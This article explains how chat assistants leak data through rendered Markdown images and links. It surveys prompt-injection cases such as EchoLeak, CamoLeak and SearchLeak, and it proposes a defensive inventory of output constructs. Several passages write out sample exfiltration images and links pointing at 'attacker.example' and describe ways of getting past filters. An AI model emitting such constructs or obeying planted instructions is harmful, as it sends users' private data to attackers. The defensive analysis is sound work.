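# Filtering links and images in language model outputs to prevent data exfiltration

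## How an assistant's answer can carry private data out

Data exfiltration means moving private data to a party who should not have it. In applications built on large language models, the systems behind chat assistants such as ChatGPT and Claude, this can happen when an answer is displayed. The application turns parts of the model's text into pictures, links and diagrams, some of which make the user's browser contact other computers. An attacker who can influence what the model writes can therefore make the browser send a request containing private data to the attacker's computer. The security researcher Johann Rehberger reported this flaw to OpenAI and Microsoft in early 2023, as he recounts in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* on his blog, Embrace The Red. *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems* (2025) calls the image version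 well known. A filter against such leaks removes or disables the dangerous parts of an answer before the browser acts on them, and ideally leaves the rest unchanged.

### From text to web request

Chat assistants commonly write their answers in Markdown, a set of conventions for marking up plain text that John Gruber released in 2004. Asterisks around a word mark emphasis, a hyphen at the start of a line marks a list item, and the text is readable even without conversion. *CommonMark Spec* (MacFarlane, 2024) sets out the rules in detail. A link is a label in square brackets followed by an address in parentheses. An image is written almost the same way, but with an exclamation mark in front.

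The renderer is the software that turns the model's text into what the user sees. It typically converts Markdown into HTML and passes the result to the browser. An output construct is any piece of the output that the renderer treats as more than plain text, such as an image, a link, a diagram or a block of HTML. Links and images differ by only one character in Markdown, but the browser follows a link only when someone clicks it. An image becomes an `img` element, and the browser ordinarily fetches the picture without asking anyone.

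A browser needs a web address, or URL, to fetch anything. In `https://shop.example/shoes/red?size=42#reviews`, the host, `shop.example`, identifies the server to contact. The path, `/shoes/red`, identifies the resource to fetch, and the query, `?size=42`, passes extra values to the server, here a shoe size. Mozilla's *What is a URL?* notes that paths once matched real folders on a disk but are now mostly an abstraction. A server's owner can therefore accept any path or query, including one that a model has just generated. The host can also carry data, because the owner of `attacker.example` can receive requests for every name beneath it, such as `someword.attacker.example`.

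Browsers never include the part of a URL after the `#`, called the fragment, in the request. This makes the fragment harmless in an image address. In a link, it can still leak data, because once the user opens the attacker's page, a script on that page can read the fragment and send it on.

The path and query in a web address reach the server, and servers keep records of them. The access log of Apache, a widely used web server program, records all requests the server processes, according to Apache's *Log Files*. In the common format, each line holds the visitor's network address, the time, and the full request with its path and query. HTTPS encrypts the request so that others can't read it in transit, but the receiving server has to decrypt it to answer. OWASP's *Information exposure through query strings in url* lists web logs among the places where query values appear with or without HTTPS.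 This is normally harmless because the address contains nothing secret, so a leak depends on getting secret data into the address.

### One leak, step by step

Suppose a sales manager asks an email assistant to summarise the morning's messages. The mailbox contains a confidential quote of 48,000 euros to a customer and a message from a stranger.

1. The stranger's message contains text meant for the model, perhaps in type too small for a person to notice. The text tells the model to end its summary with a picture and to put the price from the quote into the picture's address.
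2. The assistant loads both messages into the model's context, the text the model has available when it writes.
3. The model writes a correct summary and adds one image at the end: `![](https://attacker.example/p.png?data=48000)`.
4. The renderer converts this into an `img` element. The browser sends `attacker.example` a request for `/p.png?data=48000`.
5. The attacker's server adds a line to its log: `203.0.113.7 - - [04/Dec/2026:09:14:02 +0000] "GET /p.png?data=48000 HTTP/1.1" 404 196`. The attacker opens the log and reads the price.

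The number 404 in that line is the standard code for "not found". The picture never existed, and the attack did not need one because the request itself carried the data. The security company Checkmarx recorded a demonstration in which the request went out even though no image appeared on screen. An attacker who wants to avoid a broken-image icon can supply a real but invisible picture. Roman Samoilenko's 2023 attack on ChatGPT used a single-pixel image, as the software developer Simon Willison (2023) described in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*.

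The model in this example had no tool for browsing the web or sending mail. It only wrote text, and the browser sent the data. Turning off an assistant's internet tools, or requiring the user to approve every tool call, therefore does not prevent this kind of leak. *Takedown* (2025), a study of attacks on coding assistants, also notes that renderers that load outside resources do so without user approval.

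Some assistants carry summaries of past conversations into each new one, so the context can hold a lot about a person before any document is added. In *The Memory Heist*, Paul (2026) got Claude to leak his full name, his employer and the answers to his security questions while the conversation on screen looked ordinary. His attack used Claude's web-browsing tool instead of an image, but it also sent the data out in the addresses of requested pages. Anthropic has since closed the gap he used.

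### Planted instructions and the lethal trifecta

The example begins with an indirect prompt injection, in which the assistant reads content containing hidden instructions and follows them as if the user had given them. *Exploiting Web Search Tools of AI Agents for Data Exfiltration* (2025) lists tool outputs, web pages and documents as typical places for these instructions. In a direct injection, the attacker types the instructions into the chat box.

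A model may follow instructions in a stranger's email because of how it receives its input, as Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*. The developer's instructions, the user's question and the email all end up in one long sequence of tokens, the word fragments that a model processes, and models cannot reliably work out how much weight an instruction deserves from where it came from. Developers can't simply train models to stop following instructions in text, because following them is what makes models useful. Training can reduce the problem, but Rahman and Kim (2026) found in *The Framing Gap* that attackers who reframed their request could still extract a secret from an agent with a published training-based defence. Criminals are also developing tools for such attacks, according to Underhill (2026) in *Cybercriminals Turn to Indirect Prompt Injection Attacks*.

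An attacker can steal data through an assistant that has access to private data, reads content the attacker can influence, and has some way to communicate outward. Willison calls this combination the "lethal trifecta." Without private data there is nothing to steal, without untrusted content the attacker has no way to give the model instructions, and without an outward channel the model can still collect private data but can't send it to the attacker.

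A chat window that displays remote images provides, by itself, a way to send private data out. After a leak of this kind turned up in GitHub Copilot Chat, a programming assistant, Willison (2024) stated a general rule that a chat interface has this vulnerability if it handles both private and untrusted data and supports Markdown images. GitHub fixed the problem by disabling images from untrusted domains.

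That choice of fix is typical, mostly for practical reasons. The product usually needs access to private data, as an email assistant needs to read email. Keeping out untrusted content is hard when anybody who knows an address can send a message to it. The outward channel is generally the easiest of the three to remove, as Willison argues on his page of such incidents, *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*. Ordinary code can compare a host name with a list and get the same answer every time, whatever wording the attacker chose, but no comparable test exists for whether a paragraph of English is trying to mislead a model. Willison's essay on the trifecta lists well over a dozen leaks in commercial products and notes that the vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by blocking the outward channel.

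Filtering links and images closes this channel but leaves the model as easy to mislead as before. Planted text can still make a summary false or suppress something the user needed to know. If the assistant can also send email or call other services, data can leave by those routes, which a filter on displayed output doesn't block. Embrace The Red similarly notes that OpenAI's measures against URLs that leak data address the channel and aren't presented as a defence against prompt injection. The filter still limits the damage even when every defence inside the model has failed.

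### Zero-click and one-click leaks

The sales manager in the example leaked the price just by asking for a summary. A leak that needs no click or approval beyond ordinary use of the assistant is called a zero-click leak. VerSprite's *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue* describes a flaw in a coding assistant. The user opens a file and asks for an analysis of it, and a comment in the file triggers the leak. VerSprite counts this as zero-click, which is reasonable because people install the assistant to analyse files. PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data* describes the same pattern in HuggingChat, another chat application, where the planted text could be in a document or a web page.

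In a one-click leak, the model writes a link whose address contains private data, and the user sends the data by clicking it. Markdown makes this easy to miss because the reader sees only the link's label, such as "Open the full report", and not the address unless they look for it. When the user clicks, the application can show the full address and ask whether to continue, but it has no such chance with an image, which loads without a click.

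A link can leak data without a click if it appears in an app that generates link previews. Messaging apps such as Slack and Telegram automatically fetch a title or picture to show beneath a message that contains a link, and that fetch sends the complete address, including any private data in it. PromptArmor warns that an assistant that talks to its user through a messaging app can therefore leak data as soon as its message arrives. In a plain web chat, the same link would leak data only if the user clicked it. A filter's author therefore needs to know which renderer will receive the output. Willison (2024) notes a partial remedy for Slack, where an app that posts messages can turn previews off.

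Users often can't tell from reading an answer that it has leaked data. *Silent Egress* (2026) tested agents that preview links automatically and found that the visible response stayed harmless while a background request sent the data out. A check that only searches the displayed text for secrets or suspicious wording would miss such a leak.

### The defences and their two errors

Two of the four common defences are sanitisers and allowlists. A sanitiser is code that removes or rewrites risky constructs before the application displays them. GitHub, for example, sanitises user content after converting it from Markdown to HTML. This order helps because Markdown programs handle unusual cases differently, and the sanitiser can check the same HTML that the browser will receive. An allowlist is a list of the only hosts or addresses from which loading is permitted.

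A content security policy (CSP) is a rule that a website sends to the browser, naming the hosts from which the page may load images, scripts and other resources. The browser enforces it, so it can block an image that the sanitiser missed, but it does not stop a user from following a link. Microsoft used a CSP in May 2023 to stop images from loading in Bing Chat. An image proxy is a server that fetches images for the user's browser. It hides the user's network address from the outside host, but it helps prevent leaks only if it also refuses to fetch some URLs. If it requests `attacker.example/p.png?data=48000`, the attacker's log still records the price.

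A filter can let through a construct that carries private data (a missed leak), or remove or interrupt a harmless one (a false block). The two error rates should not be combined into a single accuracy figure, because harmless constructs turn up in the course of normal work, while attackers choose their cases. A false block rate of one per cent means that roughly one harmless link or image in a hundred is blocked. But if one form of URL in a hundred gets past the filter, attackers will look for it and use it every time, which is why Willison calls 99 per cent a failing grade in application security.

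This is a reason to filter strictly, and the strictest filter is easy to write. It deletes every image and link, so nothing in the answer can cause a request. That may well be the right choice for a tool that only needs to return plain text, but most assistants would lose a lot of useful output. A research assistant's links are its citations, and without them readers can't quickly check a claim against its source. A data assistant would lose any chart it delivers as an image, and a shopping assistant could no longer show the product.

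When an assistant asks users about every doubtful address, they learn to click through the warnings without reading them. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) gives this as one reason for not relying on a rigid list of trusted sites. People visit far more of the web than any short list covers, so the warnings are frequent and mostly false alarms. A filter that wrongly flags too many addresses can therefore cause missed leaks, because the one warning that matters looks like all the others.

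## Cases in which remote images leaked data, 2023 to 2026

In early 2023, chat assistants loaded any image the model wrote, from any host. From 2025 on, most of the well-known leaks came from products that already had a filter, and researchers put most of their work into bypassing it. These later cases are more useful to someone building a filter. The early ones still matter, partly because vendors reacted to them differently and partly because one of the first fixes allowed a host that researchers used three years later to extract data from a related product.

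### Images from any host

Rehberger reported the leak in Bing Chat, Microsoft's search assistant, on 8 April 2023. Bing Chat could read the web page the user was visiting, so an attacker could plant instructions in a comment or an advertisement on that page. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* demonstrates the attack on a page that also contained a secret. After two more turns of conversation, the model wrote an image whose address contained the secret and a 200-character summary of the page and the conversation. A filter that is strict only for the first answer after the model reads a risky page would have missed this leak.

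Microsoft told Rehberger on 15 June 2023 that it had put a fix in place. The fix is sometimes dated to May 2023, but that does not match his timeline. His old tests no longer worked, and the page now had a CSP that allowed images from four hosts: `th.bing.com`, `www.bing.com`, `edgeservices.bing.com` and `r.bing.com`. Microsoft could not turn images off entirely because users could ask Bing Chat to create pictures. Rehberger notes that Microsoft may have taken other measures that he couldn't see from outside.

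By contrast, when Rehberger reported the same flaw in ChatGPT on 9 April 2023, OpenAI eventually told him that displaying images was a feature and that it planned no changes, as he recounts in *ChatGPT Plugins*. The flaw could expose the user's conversation. SecurityWeek credits both Rehberger and Samoilenko, who found the leak independently that spring. It reports that an attacker's text could reach ChatGPT if the user asked for a summary of the attacker's web page or pasted in text copied from one. Samoilenko's version relied on pasting, with a script on his page that added instructions to any text a visitor copied, as Willison explains.

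Anthropic fixed the same leak in Claude while ChatGPT still had it, according to Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed*. OpenAI's first repair came in December 2023, more than eight months after the report. The day before, Rehberger had demonstrated the flaw live on a consenting victim, and his server had received the details of the victim's conversation. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* describes the repair as imperfect but a step in the right direction. The ChatGPT page could still display outside images, but it first checked with an OpenAI server whether each one was "safe". Willison (2023), in a link-blog entry of the same title, called this design a bit weird. One practical weakness is that every program that displays ChatGPT's answers has to make this check. OpenAI has since developed more elaborate address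 checks.

As late as 2024, Google AI Studio, a website where developers try out Google's Gemini models, displayed images from any host without any check between the model's output and the browser's request. Rehberger found and reported the flaw, and Google then fixed it. Checkmarx also found that image requests leaked data from Google Gemini and Microsoft Copilot Chat.

### EchoLeak: a second way to write a link

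Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office programs, retrieves material that seems relevant from the user's mailbox, stored files, internal sites and Teams chats before it answers a question. According to the timeline in *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025), researchers at Aim Labs, part of the security company Aim Security, built an attack on Copilot and reported it to Microsoft in January 2025. The attacker only had to send the victim an email. The victim didn't have to open it, because the attack began when Copilot retrieved the email while answering an ordinary question.

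Copilot would rarely retrieve an email about one narrow subject, so the researchers wrote a long one with many sections, each under a heading on a common office topic such as leave of absence, and repeated the instructions in every section. *Breaking down 'EchoLeak', the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025), their account of the attack, lists the data it could reach: the whole chat history, everything Copilot had retrieved, and details loaded in advance, such as the names of the user and the organisation.

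Microsoft had three defences in place. The first was a classifier trained to detect planted instructions and keep them from reaching Copilot. The researchers got past it by phrasing their instructions as requests to the email's recipient and never mentioning an assistant. Ravia argues that such text is inherently hard to detect because it is normal for an email to ask an employee to do something.

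The second obstacle was a filter on Copilot's answers, which removed links and images pointing outside the organisation. It looked for the common form, with the address in parentheses directly after the label. Markdown also has a reference style, in which the address stands on a line of its own:

```
[Open the full report][1]

[1]: https://attacker.example/?data=48000
```

The reader sees the same clickable label either way. Markdown also permits shorter versions, in which the second pair of brackets is empty or missing and the label serves as the reference. Ravia reports that the filter removed none of these. The renderer recognised every form as a link, but the filter recognised only one. The same trick worked for images, so the victim no longer had to click.

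The browser still refused to load the image, because the third obstacle was a CSP and `attacker.example` was not on it. Ravia prints the policy's list of image hosts. Leaving out repetitions, it has 29 entries, and 11 of them are wildcards that admit every host name under a domain. The researchers went through this list looking for a host that would fetch some other address on request. They first found a SharePoint function for embedding outside content, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. Then they found a Teams function that fetches previews of web pages and has no such condition. The image address took roughly this form, with invented names:

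`https://trusted.example/preview?url=https://attacker.example/48000`

The browser sent the request because the host was on the list. The trusted server then read the second address from the query and fetched it, which sent the price to the attacker. A CSP can't block this second request, because it restricts only the browser and the request comes from a server.

Separately, the wildcard for SharePoint includes pages that strangers control, even though it looks like an entry for "our own service". Every organisation that uses SharePoint Online gets its own name under `sharepoint.com`, and an attacker can sign up too.

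Microsoft began work on a fix in April 2025, deployed it on its servers in May and published the flaw as CVE-2025-32711 on 11 June. (A CVE number is the standard public identifier for a security flaw.) According to Reddy and Gujral, Copilot now strips reference-style links and embedded images from incoming outside content, and customers reportedly got options to keep outside messages out of Copilot in some situations. Stripping this content limits what planted text can contain, but it can't replace a check on the answer, because a model can write a link in any style without having seen an example in the email.

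Ravia calls EchoLeak the first zero-click flaw in a major AI application. Taken literally, that is doubtful, since the images in Bing Chat also loaded without a click. But Ravia says that in earlier demonstrations, either the user had to point the assistant at the attacker's material or the attacker could extract only very restricted data. That seems a fair description of what changed, since anyone can email a victim, whereas an attack through a web page requires the victim to visit it.

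### CamoLeak: data in the order of the pictures

GitHub had stronger protection than a list of hosts. Its CSP allowed images only from domains that GitHub owns. Images from elsewhere came through Camo, GitHub's image proxy, which restricted the addresses it would fetch.

When someone saves Markdown with an outside image, GitHub replaces the image's address with one for Camo, its image proxy. The new address includes a signature, a code computed from the original address with a key that only GitHub has. When a browser requests the image, Camo checks the signature and fetches nothing if it is wrong. This blocks the usual form of the leak, in which a model adds a secret to an image address, as in `data=48000`. The model can't compute a signature for that address, and getting one from GitHub in advance would require the attacker to know the secret already.

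In June 2025 Omer Mayraz of Legit Security found a way around this in GitHub Copilot Chat, which he describes in the company's *CamoLeak*. He set up one image address on his own server for each letter, digit and symbol, had GitHub sign them all through its public API, and put the list into the planted text. The model could then spell out a secret by displaying the images in order. To leak a price of 48,000 euros, it would display the images for 4, 8, 0, 0 and 0, and the attacker's server would receive the requests in that order.

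GitHub had signed every image address used in this attack, and none of the addresses contained private data. Instead, the model encoded the data in its choice and order of images. A filter that searches addresses for secrets or long, random-looking strings would find nothing suspicious. The images were transparent and one pixel in size, so the victim did not see them.

Mayraz had the model add a new random number to the end of each address so that repeated characters would reach the attacker. Without it, a browser or proxy that had just fetched the picture for 0 might reuse a saved copy, and the attacker would receive 480. Camo evidently accepted the altered addresses, so the signature did not protect the whole address.

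Mayraz planted the text in a pull request, a proposed change to a project's code that others are asked to review. He put it in a comment that doesn't show on the page, a feature GitHub officially supports. When someone asked Copilot about the pull request, Copilot received the instructions and worked with that person's permissions, including access to private projects. SecurityWeek's *GitHub Copilot Chat Flaw Leaked Data From Private Repositories* reports that in his demonstrations he obtained the description of an unpatched vulnerability from a private project and had Copilot search the victim's code for access keys to Amazon's cloud service. Spelling out data at one image request per character is slow, and a large program would take an enormous number of images, but a 40-character key takes only 40.

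By 14 August 2025, GitHub had fixed the flaw by turning off images in Copilot Chat completely. It had apparently done the same after the earlier Copilot Chat leak. According to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, Rehberger reported that leak on 25 February 2024, GitHub confirmed a fix on 12 June, and the assistant then seemed to stop displaying Markdown images. A year later, Mayraz found images working in the version on GitHub's site. Either that version never had the fix or GitHub had brought images back. Both happen often enough in large products that a team should repeat its old leak tests on every version it ships.

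Several press reports, including VPNCentral's *Hackers exploited GitHub Copilot flaw to exfiltrate sensitive data from private repositories*, wrongly attach the number CVE-2025-59145 to CamoLeak. MITRE's official record for that number, *color-name@2.0.1 contains malware after npm account takeover* (2025), describes a JavaScript package that someone had infected with malware. Legit Security's own account of CamoLeak gives no CVE number.

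### ForcedLeak: an allowed domain with a new owner

Agentforce is Salesforce's system for building AI agents that work with a company's customer records. Salesforce's Web-to-Lead feature can turn the details that prospective customers enter in a form on a company's public website into sales leads. Anyone can fill in the form, so researchers at Noma, a security company, wrote instructions into a submission. When Agentforce later processed that lead, it followed the instructions and put data about other leads into the address of an image. In the instructions quoted in Security Affairs' *ForcedLeak flaw in Salesforce Agentforce exposes CRM data via Prompt Injection*, the researchers asked for the leads' email addresses.

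Salesforce had a content security policy (CSP) to block such leaks, but it allowed `my-salesforce-cms.com` and all its subdomains, and that domain's registration had expired. According to Willison, Noma's researchers registered the domain and received the lead data in their server's logs. Salesforce Ben quotes Noma as saying that exfiltration "would have been impossible" without this oversight.

EchoLeak required days of searching through Microsoft's services for one that would forward a request. ForcedLeak needed no relay because the attacker owned the allowed host. Salesforce's policy was presumably correct when written and became dangerous later, although nobody had changed it, so a code review would not have found the problem. Preventing this requires regularly checking who owns each domain on the list, or restricting the list to domains whose renewal the company controls.

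Noma reported the flaw on 28 July 2025, and Salesforce acknowledged it three days later. Salesforce took back the expired domain and, on 8 September, began enforcing an allowlist of trusted URLs for its agents. The company said this should prevent planted instructions from causing malicious links to be "called or generated" (The Hacker News, 2025). The allowlist goes further than repairing the CSP because it also covers links.

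### SearchLeak: an image that loaded before the filter ran

SearchLeak, which the security company Varonis found in Microsoft 365 Copilot Enterprise Search, began with a link to Microsoft's own site. The link opened Copilot's search page with a query already filled in, and Copilot immediately began following the query as instructions (Taler, 2026, *SearchLeak*). Copilot could search everything the victim could, including email, calendar entries, and files in SharePoint and OneDrive. The demonstration stole the subject line of an email, and subject lines often contain one-time security codes.

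Varonis and most press reports call this a one-click attack, but it differs from a one-click leak, in which the click itself sends the data. Here the victim clicked a link to a genuine Microsoft address in an email or chat message. The link contained only instructions, and the private data left afterwards in an image that loaded automatically. A confirmation box on links in Copilot's answers would have made no difference, because the link the victim clicked was not in those answers.

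Microsoft knew that Copilot's answers could contain harmful HTML, so it wrapped them in a code block, which makes the browser show HTML as text instead of acting on it. But Copilot's answers, like those of most chat assistants, arrive piece by piece while the model is still writing, and the wrapping happened only at the end.

1. The model wrote an image element as part of its answer.
2. The page displayed the unfinished answer, and the browser requested the image immediately.
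3. The model finished, and the protection turned the image element into harmless text.

The data had already leaked by the third step. A tester who checked only finished answers would have seen the filter work every time. Taler advises sanitising output at the moment the page renders it, because a browser loads images without waiting for the final version.

The remaining defense was the CSP, which allowed `*.bing.com`. Bing can search for pictures similar to one at a given address, and its server has to fetch that picture to do so. The model's image therefore pointed to Bing, with the attacker's address and the stolen subject line in the query, and Bing's server sent the subject line to the attacker when it tried to fetch the picture. EchoLeak had used Teams in the same way. The `*.bing.com` entry appears in the list that Ravia had published a year earlier, and `www.bing.com`, the host that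 carried the request, was one of the four that Microsoft had allowed in Bing Chat in 2023.

Microsoft's entry for the flaw, *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), is numbered CVE-2026-42824 and dated 4 June 2026. Microsoft had mitigated the flaw by the time the press reported it in mid-June. Microsoft rated it critical but scored it only 6.5 on the ten-point CVSS severity scale, while the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to The Hacker News' *One-Click Microsoft 365 Copilot Flaw Could Have Let Attackers Steal Emails* (2026). The scores may differ because only Microsoft's takes into account that the user has to click. The 6.5 score in Exploit Intel's *CVE-2026-42824* includes a required user action, and removing that condition from the formula gives exactly 7.5.

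### ReLeak: Bing again

The team that found EchoLeak now works as Cato AI Labs, after Cato Networks bought Aim Security in September 2025. On 3 December 2026, it published *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026), which describes three more zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot. Like EchoLeak, each starts with an email that the victim need not open and that Copilot retrieves while answering an ordinary question. *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief* (Faisal, 2026) reports that Microsoft's classifier for planted instructions stopped none of the three attacks.

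One of the three used an image. Copilot put confidential data into an image address, the browser loaded the image, and Bing's service passed the data on to the attacker's server. Faisal doesn't mention the CSP, but it probably blocked direct requests to that server, since the attacker would otherwise have had little reason to go through Bing. Nexo Causal's *ReLeak* (2026) describes the same path.

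Cato reported its findings between 29 July and 20 August 2026, at least seven weeks after Microsoft's entry for SearchLeak, so Microsoft's fix for SearchLeak had not stopped Bing from carrying data out of Copilot. Microsoft may have closed the function that Varonis used but left another open, or it may have fixed the streaming problem without changing Bing. In either case, if a filter's policy allows a whole family of hosts, its author has to find every function on them that fetches outside addresses, because an attacker needs only one.

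Microsoft patched the image attack on 15 November 2026. Faisal gives its number as CVE-2026-124115, although two of the three ReLeak numbers were still marked "reserved" in the public register at the time, without details. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) lists the same three patch dates.

The other two attacks didn't use displayed images, so even a perfect filter on Copilot's displayed answers would not have stopped them. In one, Copilot saved a document containing a link with private data in it, and the data leaked when Microsoft's background processing opened the file (CVE-2026-124132, patched on 11 November). In the other, code that Copilot ran in its supposedly isolated Python environment sent the data straight to an outside server (CVE-2026-78501, patched on 17 September).

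### The cases by failed defence

EchoLeak and SearchLeak appear twice in this table because each got past two controls on the output.

| Defence that failed | Case | How the request got through | Fixed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None in place | Bing Chat | Images loaded from any host | 15 June 2023 |
| None in place | ChatGPT | Images loaded from any host | Partly, December 2023 |
| None in place | Google AI Studio | Images loaded from any host | 2024 |
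| Removal of outside links and images | EchoLeak | The filter did not recognise reference-style Markdown | May 2025 |
| Code block around the answer | SearchLeak | The browser loaded the image before the wrapping | By mid-June 2026 |
| Image proxy with signed addresses | CamoLeak | The model spelled out data with addresses signed in advance | 14 August 2025 |
| CSP | EchoLeak | An allowed Teams host fetched the attacker's address | May 2025 |
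| CSP | ForcedLeak | An allowed domain had expired, and the researchers registered it | 8 September 2025 |
| CSP | SearchLeak | An allowed Bing host fetched the attacker's address | By mid-June 2026 |
| CSP (inferred) | ReLeak, image attack | Bing fetched the attacker's address | 15 November 2026 |

The browsers enforced these policies correctly. In all five filtered cases, including CamoLeak, the request went to a host that the policy allowed. Whoever writes a CSP in effect trusts everything the allowed hosts might do with a request. Taler recommends reviewing the list for any domain that fetches addresses supplied by users. ForcedLeak shows that it also matters who owns each domain, and CamoLeak shows that a host that checks the addresses it fetches can still leak data if the attacker can prepare acceptable addresses in advance.

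The filters that worked on the text of the answer failed instead because they examined something other than what the browser received. In EchoLeak, the renderer accepted links that the filter did not recognize as links, and in SearchLeak, the filter and the renderer worked on different stages of the answer. Only two such filters appear in the table, but I would not read much into that, because researchers publish the obstacles they got around and have less reason to describe those that made them try something else.

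The repairs took from six weeks to more than eight months. Salesforce needed 42 days from report to enforcement, and Microsoft needed 68 days for Bing Chat and between 87 and 109 for the ReLeak image attack. Customers could do little in the meantime. Ravia writes that, as far as the discoverers knew, no setting available to administrators would have prevented EchoLeak. A company that buys an assistant depends on the vendor's filter. If the company can't turn off outside content or images, its main protection is to limit which data the assistant can reach.

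### Demonstrations and known theft

Researchers carried out every attack described above, and none of the cases includes a confirmed theft from an unwilling victim. Headlines sometimes suggest otherwise. *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (Fadilpašić, 2026) refers to a ReLeak "campaign" that "looks to steal data from victims", but the hackers were Cato's research team. VPNCentral's headline also refers to hackers exploiting the GitHub flaw, but the article describes Mayraz's research.

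The vendors' statements differ in strength:

- **EchoLeak:** Microsoft confirmed that no customers were affected, according to Ravia. The public record in GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) includes an assessment by CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, that lists exploitation as "none".
- **CamoLeak:** Legit Security's account mentions GitHub's fix and gives no statement from GitHub about exploitation.
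- **ForcedLeak:** Salesforce declined to tell The Register whether anyone had abused the flaw, according to the copy of that report at Updategamers (2025).
- **SearchLeak:** CISA's assessment again lists exploitation as "none", and WinBuzzer's *Microsoft Patches Copilot SearchLeak Data-Theft Flaw* (2026) found no public evidence of active exploitation at the time of disclosure.
- **ReLeak:** Cato says it knows of no exploitation. Faisal's introduction attributes a similar assurance to Microsoft, but the body of the article attributes it to Cato.

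A vendor's statement that it knows of no exploitation is weaker evidence than a statement that it searched and found none, and the value of either depends on what the vendor could have seen. When data left through Teams or Bing, Microsoft's servers made the final request, so Microsoft may have had logs it could search for unusual outside addresses. GitHub was in a similar position with Camo. In the 2023 ChatGPT leak, the user's browser sent the request directly to the attacker's server, so OpenAI could at best have searched conversations for suspicious image addresses. Victims who noticed nothing would not have complained. EchoLeak also made Copilot omit the malicious email from its cited sources, which would have made it harder for a victim to work out afterwards what had happened.

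Aim, Varonis, Noma and Legit Security all sell security products or services, so claims such as "first" or "most dangerous" about their discoveries call for caution. Ravia's article ends by recommending Aim's own guardrails. There is less reason to doubt the technical findings, because the vendors of the affected products changed them in response, and Microsoft confirms in its own entries for EchoLeak and SearchLeak that an outsider could have obtained information over the network.

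## Listing and classifying the output constructs that cause requests

A filter can only stop constructs that its author knows about, so the author needs a list of everything in the model's output that can make a computer send a request. Each product needs its own list because renderers treat the same text differently. For example, a bare web address is ordinary text in a basic Markdown viewer and a clickable link on GitHub. In Slack, it can cause a request as soon as the message arrives.

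### Making the inventory

It is easiest to start by listing the places where the model's text ends up. Suppose the sales manager's email assistant answers in a web chat, posts a daily summary to Slack and saves reports as files, and support staff can read past conversations in a log viewer. The text then reaches four places, each with its own renderer, but a team that thinks of the product as a chat window would list only one. HackerDNA's *OWASP LLM Top 10 (2026)*, a guide from a security training company, also advises testers to trace an answer to every place it reaches, including terminals, code editors and email templates.

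For each place, the team then lists what the renderer treats as more than plain text. The Markdown software's settings show which extensions it uses and whether it accepts raw HTML. The application's code shows whether other components, such as a diagram tool, handle parts of the answer. Outsiders can do the same with more effort. *Takedown* studied eight coding agents by reading source code where available, reverse-engineering other agents and recording the messages between agent and model. To find renderers that leak data, it looked for the code that handles common markers such as backticks, square brackets and angle brackets.

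The team should also test the constructs, since it is easy to overlook something when reading code. It can write one example of each construct for each place and give every example its own URL on a server the team controls, such as `https://canary.example/slack-reference-image`. It then displays the examples with the filter off and reads the server's log. The URL in each log entry shows which construct and place caused the request, and the IP address usually shows whether it came from a browser, a preview service or the company's own server. The team should keep the server running for a few weeks because some requests happen only when someone opens an old log or file.

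Tool calls belong on a separate list. *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* (2026) includes email, posts on collaboration sites, image requests and clicked links as ways stolen data reaches an attacker. In one of its examples, the IdentityMesh attack posted private email content as a public comment on GitHub. The attacker didn't need a request from anyone's browser because anyone could read the page, so plain text is harmless only where outsiders can't see it.

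### Four questions about each construct

For every construct on the list, the team should answer four questions:

1. What makes the request, and when?
2. Who chose the host?
3. Which parts of the address did the model write?
4. Can the construct run code?

Different programs may request a link or image in the output, and at different times. The user's browser may send the request when it displays the answer, or only when the user clicks. A preview service may fetch a link when a message arrives. The assistant's own server may download an image to put it into a PDF, in which case the browser's CSP has no effect. A colleague's browser may send the request days later, when the colleague opens a log.

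The host in an address may come from the developer, the user, or text that the assistant read. If the model wrote the host and the team can't trace its source, they should assume an attacker supplied it. Some addresses contain a second address, so the inventory should record both hosts. In EchoLeak, Microsoft had approved the outer host, but the attacker had chosen the host of the address in the query.

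The third question covers the host as well as the path and query. A computer must look up a host's name before contacting it, and that lookup can reach a server run by the domain's owner. *The Anatomy of a Prompt Injection* notes that many network controls that block ordinary web requests still let data in the host name out this way. The model can also leak information without writing any part of an address. In CamoLeak, it chose among prewritten addresses and put them in order, so the team should note every choice the model makes, including which pictures it shows and how many.

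A construct that can run code is dangerous regardless of its other properties. The code can build a new address after the filter has checked the text, and it can send data without using an image or link.

### Four classes

A construct's class depends on the first and fourth answers. If the construct can run code, it is active content. If it can't, but some software sends a request without a click, it is automatically fetched content. If a request requires a click, it is a link. Everything else is inert text.

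A flaw in OpenCode, an open-source coding agent, shows why a renderer's treatment of HTML matters. Its Markdown renderer inserted any HTML in the model's answer into the page, with neither a sanitiser nor a CSP to stop scripts, according to Vulners' *CVE-2026-22813*. Any answer could therefore have run scripts in the page. PointGuard AI's *OpenCode AI UI Turns Chat Output Into Code (CVE-2026-22813)* warns that an attacker could then have run commands on the user's computer, though it reports no confirmed exploitation.

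The table below classifies common constructs. SVG is a text format for drawings, and CSS is the language that controls how web pages look. Mermaid is a tool that turns short text descriptions into diagrams.

| Construct | What makes the request, and when | Can it run code? | Class |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inline Markdown image | The browser, on display | No | Automatically fetched |
| Reference-style Markdown image | The browser, on display | No | Automatically fetched |
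| Raw HTML image | The browser, on display, if the renderer accepts HTML | Yes, through attributes such as `onerror` | Automatically fetched if a sanitiser removes those attributes, otherwise active |
| Automatic link (a bare address that the renderer makes clickable) | The browser, after a click, or a preview service on arrival | No | Link, or automatically fetched where previews are on |
| Mermaid diagram | The browser, when it draws the diagram | Depends on Mermaid's settings | Automatically fetched or active |
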